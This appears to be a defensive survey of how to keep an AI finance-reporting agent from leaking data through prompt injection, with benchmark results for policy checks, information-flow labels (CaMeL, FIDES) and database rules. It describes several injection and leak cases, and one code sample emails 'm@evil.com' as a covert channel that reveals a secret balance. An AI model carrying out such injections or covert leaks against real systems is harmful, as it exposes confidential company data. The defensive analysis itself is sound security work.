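The three rules above would not have stopped the IMAGE formula that leaked figures from Ramp's spreadsheet agent. The file rule checks only the folder, not the contents, so the agent could put the same formula in a draft report. Someone who knows that a spreadsheet cell can send a web request would have to add a rule that rejects such formulas. The email rule has a similar weakness, because a mail program may fetch images when the finance chief opens the message. Requiring plain text would fix that.

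Most gaps come from an argument that the rule's author did not consider. A recipient rule that checks only the "to" field misses a blind copy. A query rule that checks whether the text begins with SELECT allows `SELECT ... INTO`, which creates a new table in PostgreSQL. A read-only database account is firmer protection because the database itself rejects the statement. Tools that run scripts are the worst case, because the argument is a whole program and no short rule can determine what it will do. When ChatGPT's spreadsheet extension copied 12 workbooks, a policy check could have evaluated only a single script launch. The reporting agent does not need such a tool, so a rule can deny it without affecting the agent's work.

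Rules also go out of date. If the company changes auditors, the check will hold up the new firm's emails until somebody notices. Worse, it will keep offering the old firm's address for approval.

### Tests against attackers

A general assistant's tasks vary too much for a short list like the one above. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) instead has a language model write the rules for each task. The model writes the initial rules from the user's request and the list of tools, before any outside data comes in. If the task is to summarise unread emails, those rules should leave out the tool that sends email. After a tool call returns new information, the model may propose changes, because some tasks become clear only along the way. For example, if a user says "do what Alice's email asks", the agent has to read the email to find out which tools it needs.

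Letting a model change the rules after it has read untrusted text is risky. Progent therefore passes each proposed change to a solver, a program that uses logic to check whether the new rules would allow any call that the old ones forbade. Changes that would allow such a call need approval, and all others take effect at once. An attacker who deceives the rule-writing model can thus get new permissions only if somebody approves them.

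On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as both the agent and the rule-writer, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% and left task completion about the same. To imitate a careless user, the researchers automatically approved every proposed expansion in the main test, so the low rate mostly reflects how seldom the rule-writing model proposed a rule that would have let an attack through, rather than the solver's guarantee. When they froze the initial rules, attack success was 2.5%. It was zero when a person reviewed the rules, though the researchers assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness. Only 6% of the proposed changes were expansions, so a reviewer would have had few to check.

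On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, attack success fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining failures involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions resembled those of legitimate ones. Rules that people wrote using their knowledge of the tools brought the rate to zero.

Shi and colleagues excluded two of AgentDojo's attacks because such rules cannot stop them. In these attacks, planted text persuades the agent to recommend a different but genuine hotel, and booking a hotel is what the user asked for. Similarly, text in a supplier's file might persuade a finance department's reporting agent to describe the supplier's debts as low risk. The agent would write that sentence into a permitted file and send it to a permitted person, so no rule about tool calls would apply. Progent can also run as a separate server between an agent and its tools. This requires no changes to the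 agent, but it doesn't cover tools built into the agent.

In June 2026, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, who did not develop Progent, published a test of it in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both agent and rule-writer, ran eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo suites, and repeated everything three times. They also wrote an adaptive attack on the rule-writing model, in which the injected text presented the malicious action as a routine step that somebody had already authorised.

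| Suite | Attack success, no defence | With Progent | With Progent, adaptive attack | Tasks completed under attack, without and with Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% | 31.9% and 31.9% |
| Slack (workplace chat) | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% | 47.5% and 20.8% |
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 56.3% and 28.5% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% | 45.2% and 27.1% |

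The reduction is consistent with the original result but only weakly confirms it. A model this small often cannot carry out the attacker's instructions even when it tries, so a low success rate partly reflects an incompetent agent. The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one, and the researchers suspect that presenting the instruction as routine made it less forceful to the agent. If so, the attack was poor, and its failure would be little evidence that the defence works. The researchers did not use software to optimise the attack text, or try an attack that uses only tools the rules already permit, as an informed attacker probably would. The banking suite has 72 cases (eight tasks paired with nine attacker's goals), so its 1.9% amounts to one or two successful attacks per run.

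The researchers make most of these objections themselves, although they work for LaunchSafe, which builds security products on this approach. They add that the strong attackers who broke most published defences targeted filters, prompts and specially trained models. Nobody had yet run a comparable campaign against rule-based checks. A rule on recipients should be harder to beat than a filter, because an attacker has to find a harmful action that the rule allows, rather than just some text that the filter misjudges.

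The workspace figures may matter most for a reporting agent. The small model never followed an injection there, even without a defence. In one case, it was asked to count and summarise a day's appointments, read an injected instruction inside a calendar entry, and answered the question without following the instruction. The successful attacks came on tasks where the agent was already sending money or posting messages. Preparing a report mostly involves reading but ends with an email, so it falls between these two kinds of task. However, Progent needed about 15 times as many model calls, and under attack the agent completed 27.1% of its tasks instead of 45.2%.

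### Rules that catch the agent's own mistakes

Policy checks can also stop errors that involve no attacker. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, July 2026) used a simulated airline help desk in which the agent changes bookings through software tools. The airline's policy appears only in the agent's instructions, and the tools carry out any well-formed call, so the agent can cancel a booking even when the policy forbids it.

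GPT-4o-mini succeeded in 29.6% of its 250 runs. In 78% of the failures, the database ended up wrong even though no tool reported an error, so an operator reading the log would have seen no sign of trouble.

The researchers then wrote four *gates*, short functions that compare a proposed change with the current database and reject it if it breaks a policy. The cancellation gate checks the fare, the timing, the insurance and whether the passenger has already flown part of the trip. Success rose to 42.0%. In a repeat with 750 new runs, it rose from 30.8% to 43.1%. Blocking actions can raise task success because a forbidden change makes the task fail permanently, while a rejection gives the agent a reason and another try. The agent also became more consistent, getting 26% of tasks right in all five attempts, up from 8%.

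The cancellation gate helped most when customers lied. In one task, the customer lies to get a cancellation that the policy forbids. Agents succeeded in all 16 runs with the gates and in at most 1 of 16 without them. The gate checks only the booking record, so the customer's story doesn't affect it.

The four gates varied widely in quality. The cancellation gate blocked 161 calls in the audit, all correctly, and accounted for nearly all of the improvement. The baggage gate blocked 42 calls, but 40 of those were changes that the correct solution required. Both gates are deterministic, which makes their decisions consistent but not necessarily correct. The gates also let a call through if their own code crashed. That is reasonable in an experiment, but when the call would send an email with payroll figures attached, it is better to block it.

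With GPT-5.2, a much stronger model, the gates raised success from 61.2% to 71.6%, which suggests that better models still break written policies. The experiment had 250 runs and was not repeated, and the margin of error extends almost to a gain of zero. In a simulated shop whose tools already refused forbidden calls, gates did not help, and one badly written gate blocked corrected retries that the tool would have accepted. Reddy and colleagues wrote the gates from the airline's policy and tested them on a single set of 50 tasks in one industry. They did not test stating the same rules more forcefully in the instructions, which might achieve part of the gain without gates.

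A finance department could similarly use a gate that checks whether the ledger has closed for the month and refuses to email the report until it has. This would have kept the draft from reaching the auditor a week early. Gates work only for questions a program can answer from stored data, so a gate could not check whether a report's commentary is fair to the sales team.

Shlomov and colleagues tested CUGA on two sets of office tasks, with 27 and 26 tasks. With Claude Opus 4.5 as the model, the policy system raised success from 81% to 96% on one set and from 50.0% to 68.5% on the other. Much of the improvement came from added guidance, such as step-by-step procedures and warnings about unreliable tools, rather than from blocking actions. The results are therefore weak evidence of how well rules prevent harm.

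### How much legitimate work the rules block

AgentDojo is an easy test for rule-based defences because an agent can plan most of the tasks from the user's request alone. For example, to pay a named bill, the agent reads the file and sends the money. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after seeing the data. A defence can therefore score well by holding the agent to its first plan and ignoring every instruction the agent encounters while carrying it out.

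The benchmark has 60 tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life, and 560 attack cases. The tasks average 7.1 steps, about twice as many as AgentDojo's, and all of them contain legitimate instructions from third parties. For example, a bank may reply that a payment over $500 needs a one-time password, which it has just emailed. To finish the task, the agent has to find the password in the inbox and enter it, although neither step is in the user's request.

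Li and colleagues tested ten defences, among them Progent, DRIFT and CaMeL. DRIFT derives its constraints from an initial plan and uses a model to judge departures from it. Several of the researchers had also developed DRIFT, so they had no motive to make it look bad. CaMeL, which belongs with controls on data flow, turns the user's request into a fixed program before the agent reads any outside data.

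*ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, September 2026) compares its own system with Progent, DRIFT and CaMeL, which it ran on newer models. In the ActGov system, a model drafts the rules in advance from tool descriptions, ordinary tasks and records of attacks that got through. The rules refer to a fixed list of facts about each tool call, such as whether the tool sends data outside or whether an argument came from untrusted text. A solver checks every combination of these facts for cases where the rules would allow something that a stated safety requirement forbids, and the model revises the rules until no such cases remain. People then review the rules, which don't change while the agent works.

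The table gives the share of AgentDyn tasks completed when there was no attack, followed by the attack success rate. The GPT-4o and Claude figures come from Li and colleagues, and the DeepSeek and Qwen figures from Zhang and colleagues.

| Agent's model | No defence | ActGov | Progent | DRIFT | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3% / 37.8% | not tested | 6.7% / 1.7% | 30.0% / 0.8% | 0% / 0% |
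| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 71.7% / 0.9% | not tested | 16.7% / 0.2% | 28.3% / 0.2% | 0% / 0% |
| DeepSeek-v4-pro | 76.7% / 8.6% | 60.0% / 0.7% | 21.7% / 1.4% | 30.0% / 3.9% | 0% / 0% |
| Qwen3.6-flash | 66.7% / 4.6% | 66.7% / 0.4% | 15.0% / 1.1% | 3.3% / 0.0% | 0% / 0% |

The tradeoff is worst in the Claude row. Progent lowered an attack success rate that was already under 1%, while the share of tasks the agent finished fell from 72% to 17%. The protection would be more valuable against stronger attacks, and Li and colleagues concede that theirs are weak against recent models. But even the attacks they tailored to the scenarios succeeded only 3.0% of the time against undefended Claude.

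They trace Progent's losses to the number of tools, an average of 33 per task compared with about 20 in AgentDojo. The rule-writing model makes small errors in deciding which tools a task needs, and these add up over a long task until the rules block almost every useful tool.

ActGov did much better, though the comparison probably favors it. Zhang and colleagues used half of the attack cases to refine the rules and the other half for testing. The AgentDyn completion rates are all multiples of 1/60, which suggests that the test included all 60 user tasks, so the rules had probably been refined on many of the same tasks, paired with other attacks. The rival systems may also have performed below their best. CaMeL completed 20% of AgentDojo's tasks in this study, with DeepSeek-v4-pro, while its developers reported 77% with a different model. On AgentDojo, where plans are simple, DeepSeek completed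 more tasks with Progent than with ActGov (81.6% against 75.5%), but the attack success rate was 0.8% with Progent and zero with ActGov.

The month-end report is closer to AgentDojo's tasks than to AgentDyn's, since the agent uses the same few tools every month and sends the result to the same people. A request like "find out why margins fell" is more open-ended, but answering it mostly takes more reading. The rules can allow broad reading, because database permissions already limit it, and be strict about emails and files. In their AgentDojo tests, Shi and colleagues similarly allowed non-sensitive read-only tools throughout. I expect a short hand-written list of rules to block little of the reporting agent's work, but none of these studies tested an agent that writes financial reports.

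### Who writes the rules

To write good rules, a company needs both someone who understands the month-end process, usually in finance, and someone who knows that `SELECT ... INTO` creates a table, usually in IT. Together they can list what one agent with a handful of tools may do in an afternoon. With dozens of agents and hundreds of tools, maintaining the rules becomes a permanent job, so companies will be tempted to let a model do it.

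How many tasks an agent completes can depend a good deal on which model wrote its rules, even when the rules block attacks about equally well. Zhang and colleagues had three models write rules from the same prompts and examples, with no human review, and tested each set on the same agent. All three sets held attack success to 0.7% or less. The agent completed 53.3% of its AgentDyn tasks under the rules that DeepSeek-v4-pro wrote, but only about 30% under those from the two other models.

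Rules also transfer badly to unfamiliar work. Under rules refined on AgentDojo, no attack on AgentDyn succeeded, but the agent completed 10.0% of AgentDyn's tasks, compared with 60.0% under rules refined on AgentDyn itself. In the opposite direction, completion on AgentDojo fell from 75.5% to 22.4%. Rules that a vendor has tuned on general office tasks could likewise keep an agent from completing a finance department's work, so the department would need to supply examples of its own closing process.

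A solver can prove that the rules never break the written requirements, but it cannot add requirements that everyone forgot. ActGov also relies on a model to determine some facts while the agent is running, such as whether a recipient's address came from the user or from an outside document. If the model gets such a fact wrong, the rules will produce the wrong decision even though their logic is sound.

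Ravindran and Deochake (2026) write in *ToolGuardian* that "determinism is not the same as correctness". Their system classified all 20 test scenarios correctly, but they call the set small and say that they designed it together with the rules. The result shows that the rules work as intended, but not that they would cope with a real company's workflows. A simpler version of the check, without the rules that consider combinations of actions, classified 16 of the 20 correctly and let the other four through, all of them harmful workflows. In one of their examples, an agent queries a database and then updates a project page on GitHub, an outside service. Each tool is acceptable by itself, but moving the database records to the page causes harm. The three rules for the reporting agent would also miss this kind of harm, because they judge each call without regard to what the agent has already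 read.

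## How can confidential figures be kept from reaching the wrong people?

Suppose the external auditor should receive the March ledger as totals by department, without individual entries. The finance chief asks the reporting agent to send the auditor the March figures, and the agent makes three tool calls:

1. It queries the ledger for every March entry and gets 4,000 rows.
2. It adds them up and saves the totals in the drafts folder as `march_figures.xlsx`, with the 4,000 rows on a second sheet as support.
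3. It emails the file to the auditor.

The auditor now has every entry, even though no attacker was involved and the agent had permission for each call. The policy check sketched earlier allows the query because it is a plain SELECT, and the file because it goes to the right folder. It holds the email for a person to approve, but that reviewer sees an approved recipient and an ordinary file name. The reviewer might refuse if the approval screen listed what went into the file, but the check doesn't record that.

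A breach like this, made up of steps that are each permitted on their own, is a *cumulative violation*. In *Runtime Governance for AI Agents*, Kaptein, Khan and Podstavnychy (2026) describe the general case, in which a database read is harmless by itself but may be a leak when followed by an email to an outsider, and nobody can tell by inspecting either step alone. Tighter rules on single calls don't solve this, because the agent needs ledger queries to calculate the totals and emails to deliver them. The check has to take into account where the file's contents came from.

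### Labels that follow the data

*Information-flow control* attaches a label to each piece of data, passes the label on to anything made from that data, and checks the label against the recipients before sending any data. Like a policy check, it runs outside the model.

A label on the data can list the people who may read it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) combines two such labels by keeping only the names that appear on both. If the finance chief, the controller (the head of accounting) and a ledger clerk may read the ledger, and the finance chief, the controller and the head of HR may read the payroll totals, then only the finance chief and the controller may read a sheet that draws on both.

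A program can follow a number through a calculation, but it can't reliably determine which of its inputs a language model used when it wrote a sentence. The standard solution is to assume that the model used all of them. Everything the model writes inherits the combined label of everything in its conversation so far. In the auditor example, this works as follows:

1. An administrator labels the ledger rows as readable by the finance chief and the controller.
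2. The query result enters the agent's conversation, which takes on that label.
3. The agent writes the file, and the file inherits the label.
4. The agent asks to email the file. The program compares the recipient with the label, finds that the auditor is not on it, and blocks the email or refers it to a person along with the reason.

The email would have gone through if the agent had instead queried a prepared view of department totals, which the administrator had labelled as readable by the auditor too. It would have to do this in a fresh conversation, because once it has read the rows, even an email containing only totals carries the stricter label.

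A separate *integrity* label records whether data comes from a trusted source. One untrusted input makes the whole result untrusted, so a calculation that combined the company's own trusted ledger amounts with an untrusted imported sheet of industry growth rates would be untrusted. The agent may take a consequential action, such as a payment, only if it decided on that action while its conversation contained nothing untrusted. This rule stops hidden instructions from triggering such actions, while the list of readers limits the damage when something else goes wrong.

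Some designs, such as the one in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), permit a message if either the agent decided to send it in a trusted conversation or every recipient is allowed to read the contents. This is a reasonable defense against attackers, since an agent that has read nothing hostile is presumably doing what its user asked. But it would let the auditor email through, because the agent had read only the company's own ledger. To catch the agent's own mistakes, a finance department needs to check the recipients of every outgoing message.

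### CaMeL and FIDES

If the conversation takes on the labels of all the data the agent reads, importing one outside spreadsheet can stop the agent from sending anything for the rest of the task. Two research systems from 2025, CaMeL and FIDES, reduce this problem by keeping data away from the model that plans the work.

CaMeL uses two models. The planning model sees the user's request and a description of the tools, but none of the data. It writes a short program, and a second model with no access to tools handles any text that needs summarising or interpreting. For the reporting agent, the program might look like this:

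```python
totals = run_query("SELECT region, SUM(balance_due) "
                   "FROM customer_balances GROUP BY region")
industry = read_file("industry_growth.xlsx")
text = reader_model("Compare our balances with the industry",
                    totals, industry)
send_email(to="cfo@company.example", body=text)
```

An interpreter runs the program and records which inputs each value depends on. The value `text` depends on both the balances and the imported sheet, so it carries both labels, and the interpreter checks them before it sends the email. Instructions hidden in the sheet might lead the second model to write a misleading comparison, but they can't add a line to the program or change the recipient. The program can branch on what the data contain, but the planning model has to write every branch in advance.

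In FIDES, the system by Costa and colleagues, the agent chooses one step at a time, as usual. When a tool returns data that would tighten the conversation's label, the software stores the data in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The model can pass the name to another tool, open the variable and accept the tighter label, or have an isolated model answer a question about the contents. The planning model sets the form of the answer in advance, such as yes or no or a choice from a short list, and the software enforces it, which leaves an attacker almost no room to insert instructions. For example, the planning model could get a yes or no on whether an email contains a meeting request without reading the email.

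### How many tasks the agents still complete

Earlier defences did not track data. In their 2025 tests of leaks on the banking tasks, Alizadeh and colleagues also tried four defences on GPT-4o: marking off outside data with delimiters, scanning it with a detector, repeating the user's request after each tool result, and restricting the agent to the tools it seemed to need. Some stopped every leak on the 16 original tasks, but none did on the larger set of 48.

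CaMeL's developers reported that it completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an agent with no defence. According to *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), the median task took 2.82 times as many input tokens (the units of text that a model processes) and 2.73 times as many output tokens as without a defence. For a monthly report, the extra processing hardly matters, so the main drawback is the unfinished tasks.

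Later tests have mostly found a larger loss. The table shows results from Costa and colleagues' tests with GPT-4o on the banking tasks and from two 2026 studies that used all four AgentDojo settings. *SecureClaw* compares CaMeL with a system that keeps the step-by-step loop, and *SPA* tests a planning agent with and without label checks.

| Test | Protection | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
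|---|---|---|---|
| Costa and colleagues, banking | None | 98.8% | 48 |
| Costa and colleagues, banking | Label checks on an ordinary agent | 37.5% | 0 |
| Costa and colleagues, banking | FIDES with label checks | 52.5% | 0 |
| *SecureClaw*, all settings | CaMeL | 29.9% | 0 of 629 |
| *SecureClaw*, all settings | SecureClaw | 60.8% | 4 of 629 |
| *SPA*, all settings | Planning agent without label checks | 53.0% | 4 of 949 |
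| *SPA*, all settings | Planning agent with label checks | 29.0% | 0 of 949 |

The checks stopped every attack, but in *SPA* they prevented only four attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, and they nearly halved the number of tasks the agent completed. They rejected about 53% of the agent's plans, typically because a plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted input. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, such as paying a bill. Reading the file makes the conversation untrusted, so the check blocks the payment. Costa and colleagues consider most of these failures intended behavior, since a program that checks only labels can't tell a genuine bill from a planted instruction.

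Some of the loss in completed tasks comes from the models rather than the labels. *MetaPermit* (2026) ran CaMeL on the model MiniMax-M2.7 and found 5,581 cases in which the attack failed but the user's task was also left unfinished. In 4,706 of these, the agent made at most two tool calls and then stopped with a text message. CaMeL's attack success rate there was low partly because the agent did very little. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) reproduces CaMeL's own results under attack, which differ by model. CaMeL completed 1.4% of the travel cases with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 74.3% with o4-mini. In banking the gap was smaller, at 52.8% and 62.5%, and one attack in 288 succeeded.

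The checks can also reduce the number of tasks an agent completes. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, report that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halves the share of banking tasks it completes. Their own agent, which always enforces its labels, completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without the checks, and only two of 1,296 attacks on it succeeded. The system in *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) completed roughly twice as many workplace-chat tasks as CaMeL when both enforced their policies. These newer designs have reduced the losses on tasks an agent can plan in advance, but tasks that change along the way remain harder. Every GPT-4o-based defence that Li and colleagues compared on AgentDyn completed far fewer of these changing tasks than the undefended agent.

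Hiding data can also worsen the agent's judgement. In one banking task, the user asked the agent to change the password if it saw a suspicious transaction. With FIDES, the agent could see dates and amounts but not the descriptions, which an outsider could have written. It decided a large payment was suspicious and changed the password without looking at the description. Similarly, a reporting agent might call a rise in travel costs irregular because it had not read the entries that explained it.

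Kolluri and colleagues object to how these tests count failures. The tests compare an agent that must finish without human help with an undefended one that may do anything, while a company would normally send a blocked call to a person. Their agent, Prudentia, builds on FIDES but can also see the labels and rules, so it can take them into account when planning. It can ask the user to vouch for a document once instead of approving each action that follows, so an email with ten legitimate to-do items needs one request instead of ten. On AgentDojo, Prudentia completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES with no approvals, and cut the approvals needed by a factor of up to 1.9.

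None of these studies tested a month-end report. A defence should reduce task completion less there than in the banking tasks, because the agent mostly reads the company's own data and rarely has to follow instructions it finds in a file. In FIDES's office tasks, which involve more reading and summarising, completion fell from 75% without a defence to 59% with one.

### Rules on sequences of actions

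A company can catch some cumulative violations without labelling anything. The policy check keeps a list of what the agent has read in the current session and consults it before each new call:

```python
if tool == "send_email" and "general_ledger" in tables_read:
    if recipients != {"cfo@company.example"}:
        return "deny"
```

This stops the auditor email, and a programmer could add it in an afternoon. But it is cruder than a label because it also blocks an email that contains only totals. It fails if the agent saved the rows yesterday and emails the file today, since today's session contains no ledger query.

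Kaptein and colleagues propose a general form for rules that check an agent's next step. Each rule takes the agent's identity, its steps so far, the proposed next step and the state of the organisation, and returns the probability that the step would break a policy. The organisation's state matters when several agents work together. For example, a bank must keep its traders from learning what its advisory staff know about pending deals. If an advisory agent gives a task to a trading agent, the task can reveal this information even though each agent stays within its own permissions. Only a rule that covers both agents' histories can detect this. The paper includes no experiments and leaves open how to estimate the probabilities.

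### Rules inside the database

A database can work out exactly which stored rows contributed to each line of a query's result, a record known as *provenance*. Summers, Mohammed and Wu (2025), in *Please Don't Kill My Vibe*, propose rules that use it. One of their examples removes any line of a result that draws on fewer than three people if a member of the public is asking. A simplified version for customer balances could be:

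```
POLICY OVER customer_balances
CONSTRAINT count(distinct customer_id) >= 5
ON FAIL KILL QUERY
```

A rule that stops any query that would return an individual customer's balance would let the agent write whatever queries it liked without ever receiving a balance it could put into a file. The system could instead remove only the offending lines, but the remaining lines might then no longer add up to the ledger. Stopping the whole query at least makes the problem visible.

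The rule resembles the minimum group size described under database permissions, but this approach can express much more. *Data Flow Control* (Summers and Wu, 2026) gives the example of an analyst who may read advisory and trading data but not combine them in one query. Another rule requires every new expense entry to come from an existing receipt, which prevents an agent from inventing expenses. In *Agentic Data Environments* (2026), a two-line rule rejects an expense claim that deducts more than half of a restaurant bill. The database could also exclude text supplied by outsiders from any result that goes to a model.

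Recording provenance in full can make a query up to 10,000 times slower. Summers and Wu avoid this by rewriting the query so that the database checks the rule while it calculates the answer. On five database systems, including PostgreSQL and SQL Server, this added almost no time. The method covers most analytical queries but not those with negation or recursion. It also checks each query separately, so someone could still work out one person's pay by subtracting one permitted total from another. According to *Environment Steering* (2026), such rules also don't represent work done in several steps, text that a model has rewritten, or the effects of tools outside the database. If an agent is allowed to read the rows, the database can't control what the agent later puts in an email.

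### Closing the outbound channels

The simplest protection is to leave fewer ways out. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, start from the principle that untrusted text, once an agent has read it, must not be able to trigger any harmful action. This includes leaks through links and images in the agent's answer. For the reporting agent, a company could close the main channels as follows:

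- **Links and images.** The agent's emails go out as plain text, and a program removes web addresses. Charts travel as attached pictures, drawn inside the company.
- **Formulas.** The program that saves spreadsheets writes plain values and refuses any cell that the spreadsheet would treat as a formula. This would have stopped the leak from Ramp's agent.
- **Recipients.** Emails go only to a fixed list, and only the people on that list can open the shared folder.
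- **Web requests.** The agent has no web access. A scheduled program downloads the industry figures.
- **Invisible characters.** A program removes these, since they can carry hidden data.

These measures need no labels, and the report loses little more than its live links. They work against outsiders, but the auditor is an approved recipient and would still receive the raw rows.

### Separating the reader from the actor

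Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the same principle to an agent that answers questions about company data, such as how salaries are distributed in a department. The agent writes SQL to fetch the data and Python to analyse it. In the unprotected version, the model reads the query results and writes more code if it judges them insufficient, so text planted in a table could lead it to extract other data or run harmful code. In the safer version, the model writes the query and the analysis code, a program runs both, and the data never returns to the model. However, the model then can't notice that a query returned nothing useful and try another.

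The researchers also recommend running the Python code in a sandbox, an isolated environment with only the network connections it needs. This prevents the code from sending data to an outside server, but the finished answer or chart can still disclose confidential figures. They consider it impractical to have the user approve every data transfer, because each question and each attempt to answer it adds more requests.

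A month-end report suits the separated design because its queries hardly change. A program can run them and put the figures into a template, and a model without tools can write the commentary. This design could also make the ledger's description column usable again. The permissions described earlier block access to that column because outsiders write some of its text. An isolated model could read each description and return one category from a fixed list, such as "conference" or "client visit", and a program would count the results. A vendor who planted instructions in an invoice could at most put that invoice in the wrong category.

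Overly strict separation can do more harm than good. AgentDojo includes a filter that makes the model choose its tools before it starts a task. *The Same Zero* (2026) tested this filter on the banking tasks with DeepSeek's chat model. It reduced attack success from 4.3% to zero, but also reduced task completion from 86.6% to 25.0%.

### Missing labels and labels that spread

The guarantees of information-flow control and the benchmark results both depend on correct labels. Costa and colleagues gave an untrusted label to every type of field where AgentDojo plants an attack. A company doesn't know where the next attack will appear, and it has years of unlabelled exports on its shared drives. The cautious choice is to treat unlabelled files as confidential and untrusted until somebody reviews them, which will block legitimate work at first.

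Labels can also get lost between sessions. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that saves a confidential revenue forecast of $84.6 million in its long-term memory, then retrieves it in a new session three days later and writes it into an operations report. FIDES misses this because its labels end with the session. The researchers' own system, NeuroTaint, reconstructs such connections from the logs afterwards. It scored 0.928 on their test set, against 0.522 for FIDES, on a scale that combines misses and false alarms, where 1 is perfect. But they built the test set to contain the kinds of flow that NeuroTaint looks for, and an audit after the event can't undo a disclosure.

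The same thing can happen when one agent passes work to another. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) tested a database agent, a messaging agent and a coordinating agent, each with its own copy of CaMeL. A user asked the system to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. The database agent and the coordinator treated instructions planted in the database as data, but the coordinator then put the summary, with those instructions in it, into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as coming from its user and emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. On the paper's benchmark, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL and 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent. None succeeded when the agents passed data through a separate channel that preserved its origin.

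Some newer systems look for known confidential values in outgoing calls instead of relying only on labels. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) combines this with a check on what the user authorised. The system had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons, and agents using it completed at most three percentage points fewer tasks than undefended ones. However, the tested version can restore calls that the strict version would block, so the proofs don't fully cover it. The matching also misses paraphrases, such as a sentence saying that revenue should reach "about 85 million".

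The opposite problem is *label creep*, in which labels spread until the agent can hardly send anything. This happens when labels are assigned as if the model used everything it has read. If the agent reads one salary while looking for a department code, every later email carries the salary's label. *Sightline* (2026) estimates which inputs influenced each tool call and drops the labels of the others. On AgentDojo, it removed significantly more of the unnecessary labels than six of seven rival methods, and it kept the label in almost all cases where planted text had caused the call. Any such estimate can be wrong, though, so the company blocks fewer emails but is less certain that confidential figures stay protected.

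### Leaks through the agent's choices

An agent can disclose a fact without ever writing it down. If planted instructions make it send a harmless message only when the cash balance exceeds a certain amount, the arrival of the message reveals the balance's range. CaMeL blocks the direct version of this trick, because the decision to send depends on a secret. Garby and colleagues show a version that it misses, which works roughly like this:

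```python
rich = True
flag = True
if balance > threshold:
    flag = False
if flag:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "hello")
```

When the balance is high, `flag` becomes false and the line that would change `rich` never runs. CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when a line that depends on the secret changes it, so `rich` still counts as public and the email goes out. When the balance is low, no email arrives. Each run reveals one yes-or-no answer, but an attacker who can get the program to run repeatedly with different thresholds can work out the balance. In finance, even a single answer may be valuable, such as whether quarterly profit will beat the forecast.

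FIDES doesn't try to prevent leaks of this kind. Costa and colleagues explain that preventing them would essentially mean forbidding any outgoing call after the agent has read something confidential. Garby and colleagues close the gap shown above with a stricter method, which they prove correct with a proof checker. Their guarantee still allows a small leak, since whether a program finishes can reveal some information.

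Some of these leaks require no hidden instructions. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack in which an outsider shares a document containing both true and invented private details and asks the agent to tidy it up. The outsider can tell which details are true because the agent declines to delete them. A supplier could try the same with a list of a company's customers. On live email and document accounts, the attack exposed 34.7% of the private items when the agent relied on a model to recognise privacy problems. It exposed none with FlowSeal, the paper's defence, which labels records by their origin and checks every outgoing edit outside the agent's conversation. Across all the tests, FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% of the items and completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences. It still uses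 a model to judge whether a text reveals a protected record, but that model has no access to the conversation, where an attacker could mislead it.

### Figures the report is meant to disclose

The department totals come from ledger rows that the auditor may not see, so under the inheritance rules the auditor may not see the totals either. But a report is meant to reveal something about confidential data, so somebody has to decide that a total is less sensitive than the rows behind it and relax its label, which is called *declassification*. Kolluri and colleagues considered letting their agent request a relaxed label for whole pieces of data, as it can for untrusted documents. They kept approvals for individual messages instead, because whether private data may be released depends too much on the situation.

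For a monthly report, the company can make most of that decision once. An administrator defines a view of department totals, checks that no department is too small, and labels the view as readable by the auditor. The agent then prepares the auditor's version in a conversation that has access only to that view, and the finance chief's more detailed version in a separate one. The agent needs to write the commentary for each version in the same separate conversations. If it has read individual balances, a sentence such as "margins fell because one large customer stopped paying" may identify the customer, and the label on those balances will correctly stop the sentence from reaching the auditor.

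The list of permitted readers also changes over time. The auditor may see the March totals only after the books close, so the administrator should add the auditor's name to the label on the closing date, not before. These controls don't detect a wrong total, which would still have the correct label and reach only permitted readers.

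## How well do AI reviewers and activity monitoring catch harmful behaviour?

Labels and fixed rules cover only the cases someone anticipated. They can establish that the auditor may receive department totals, but not whether a finance chief who asked for "the usual report, sent round as usual" wanted the auditor to have it today. Detection tries to catch harm that nobody wrote a rule for. A company can screen documents for hidden instructions before the agent reads them, have a second model, called an *AI reviewer*, judge each tool call before it runs, and search the agent's logs afterwards for unusual activity.

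### Screening what the agent reads

A screen is usually a small model trained on examples of harmless text and known injections. The surrounding program passes it each file, web page or query result. Depending on the product, it then removes suspicious text, stops the task or adds a warning for the agent. Screens are popular because they work with any agent and are easy to install.

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked twelve published defences, ten aimed mainly at injection and two at users who try to talk a model into harmful answers. The defences included rewording the prompt, giving the model extra training, adding a separate detector, and planting a hidden signal that would reveal a hijacked model. In the adaptive attacks, programs revised their texts after seeing how the defended system responded, and more than 500 people tried to do the same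 by hand in an online contest.

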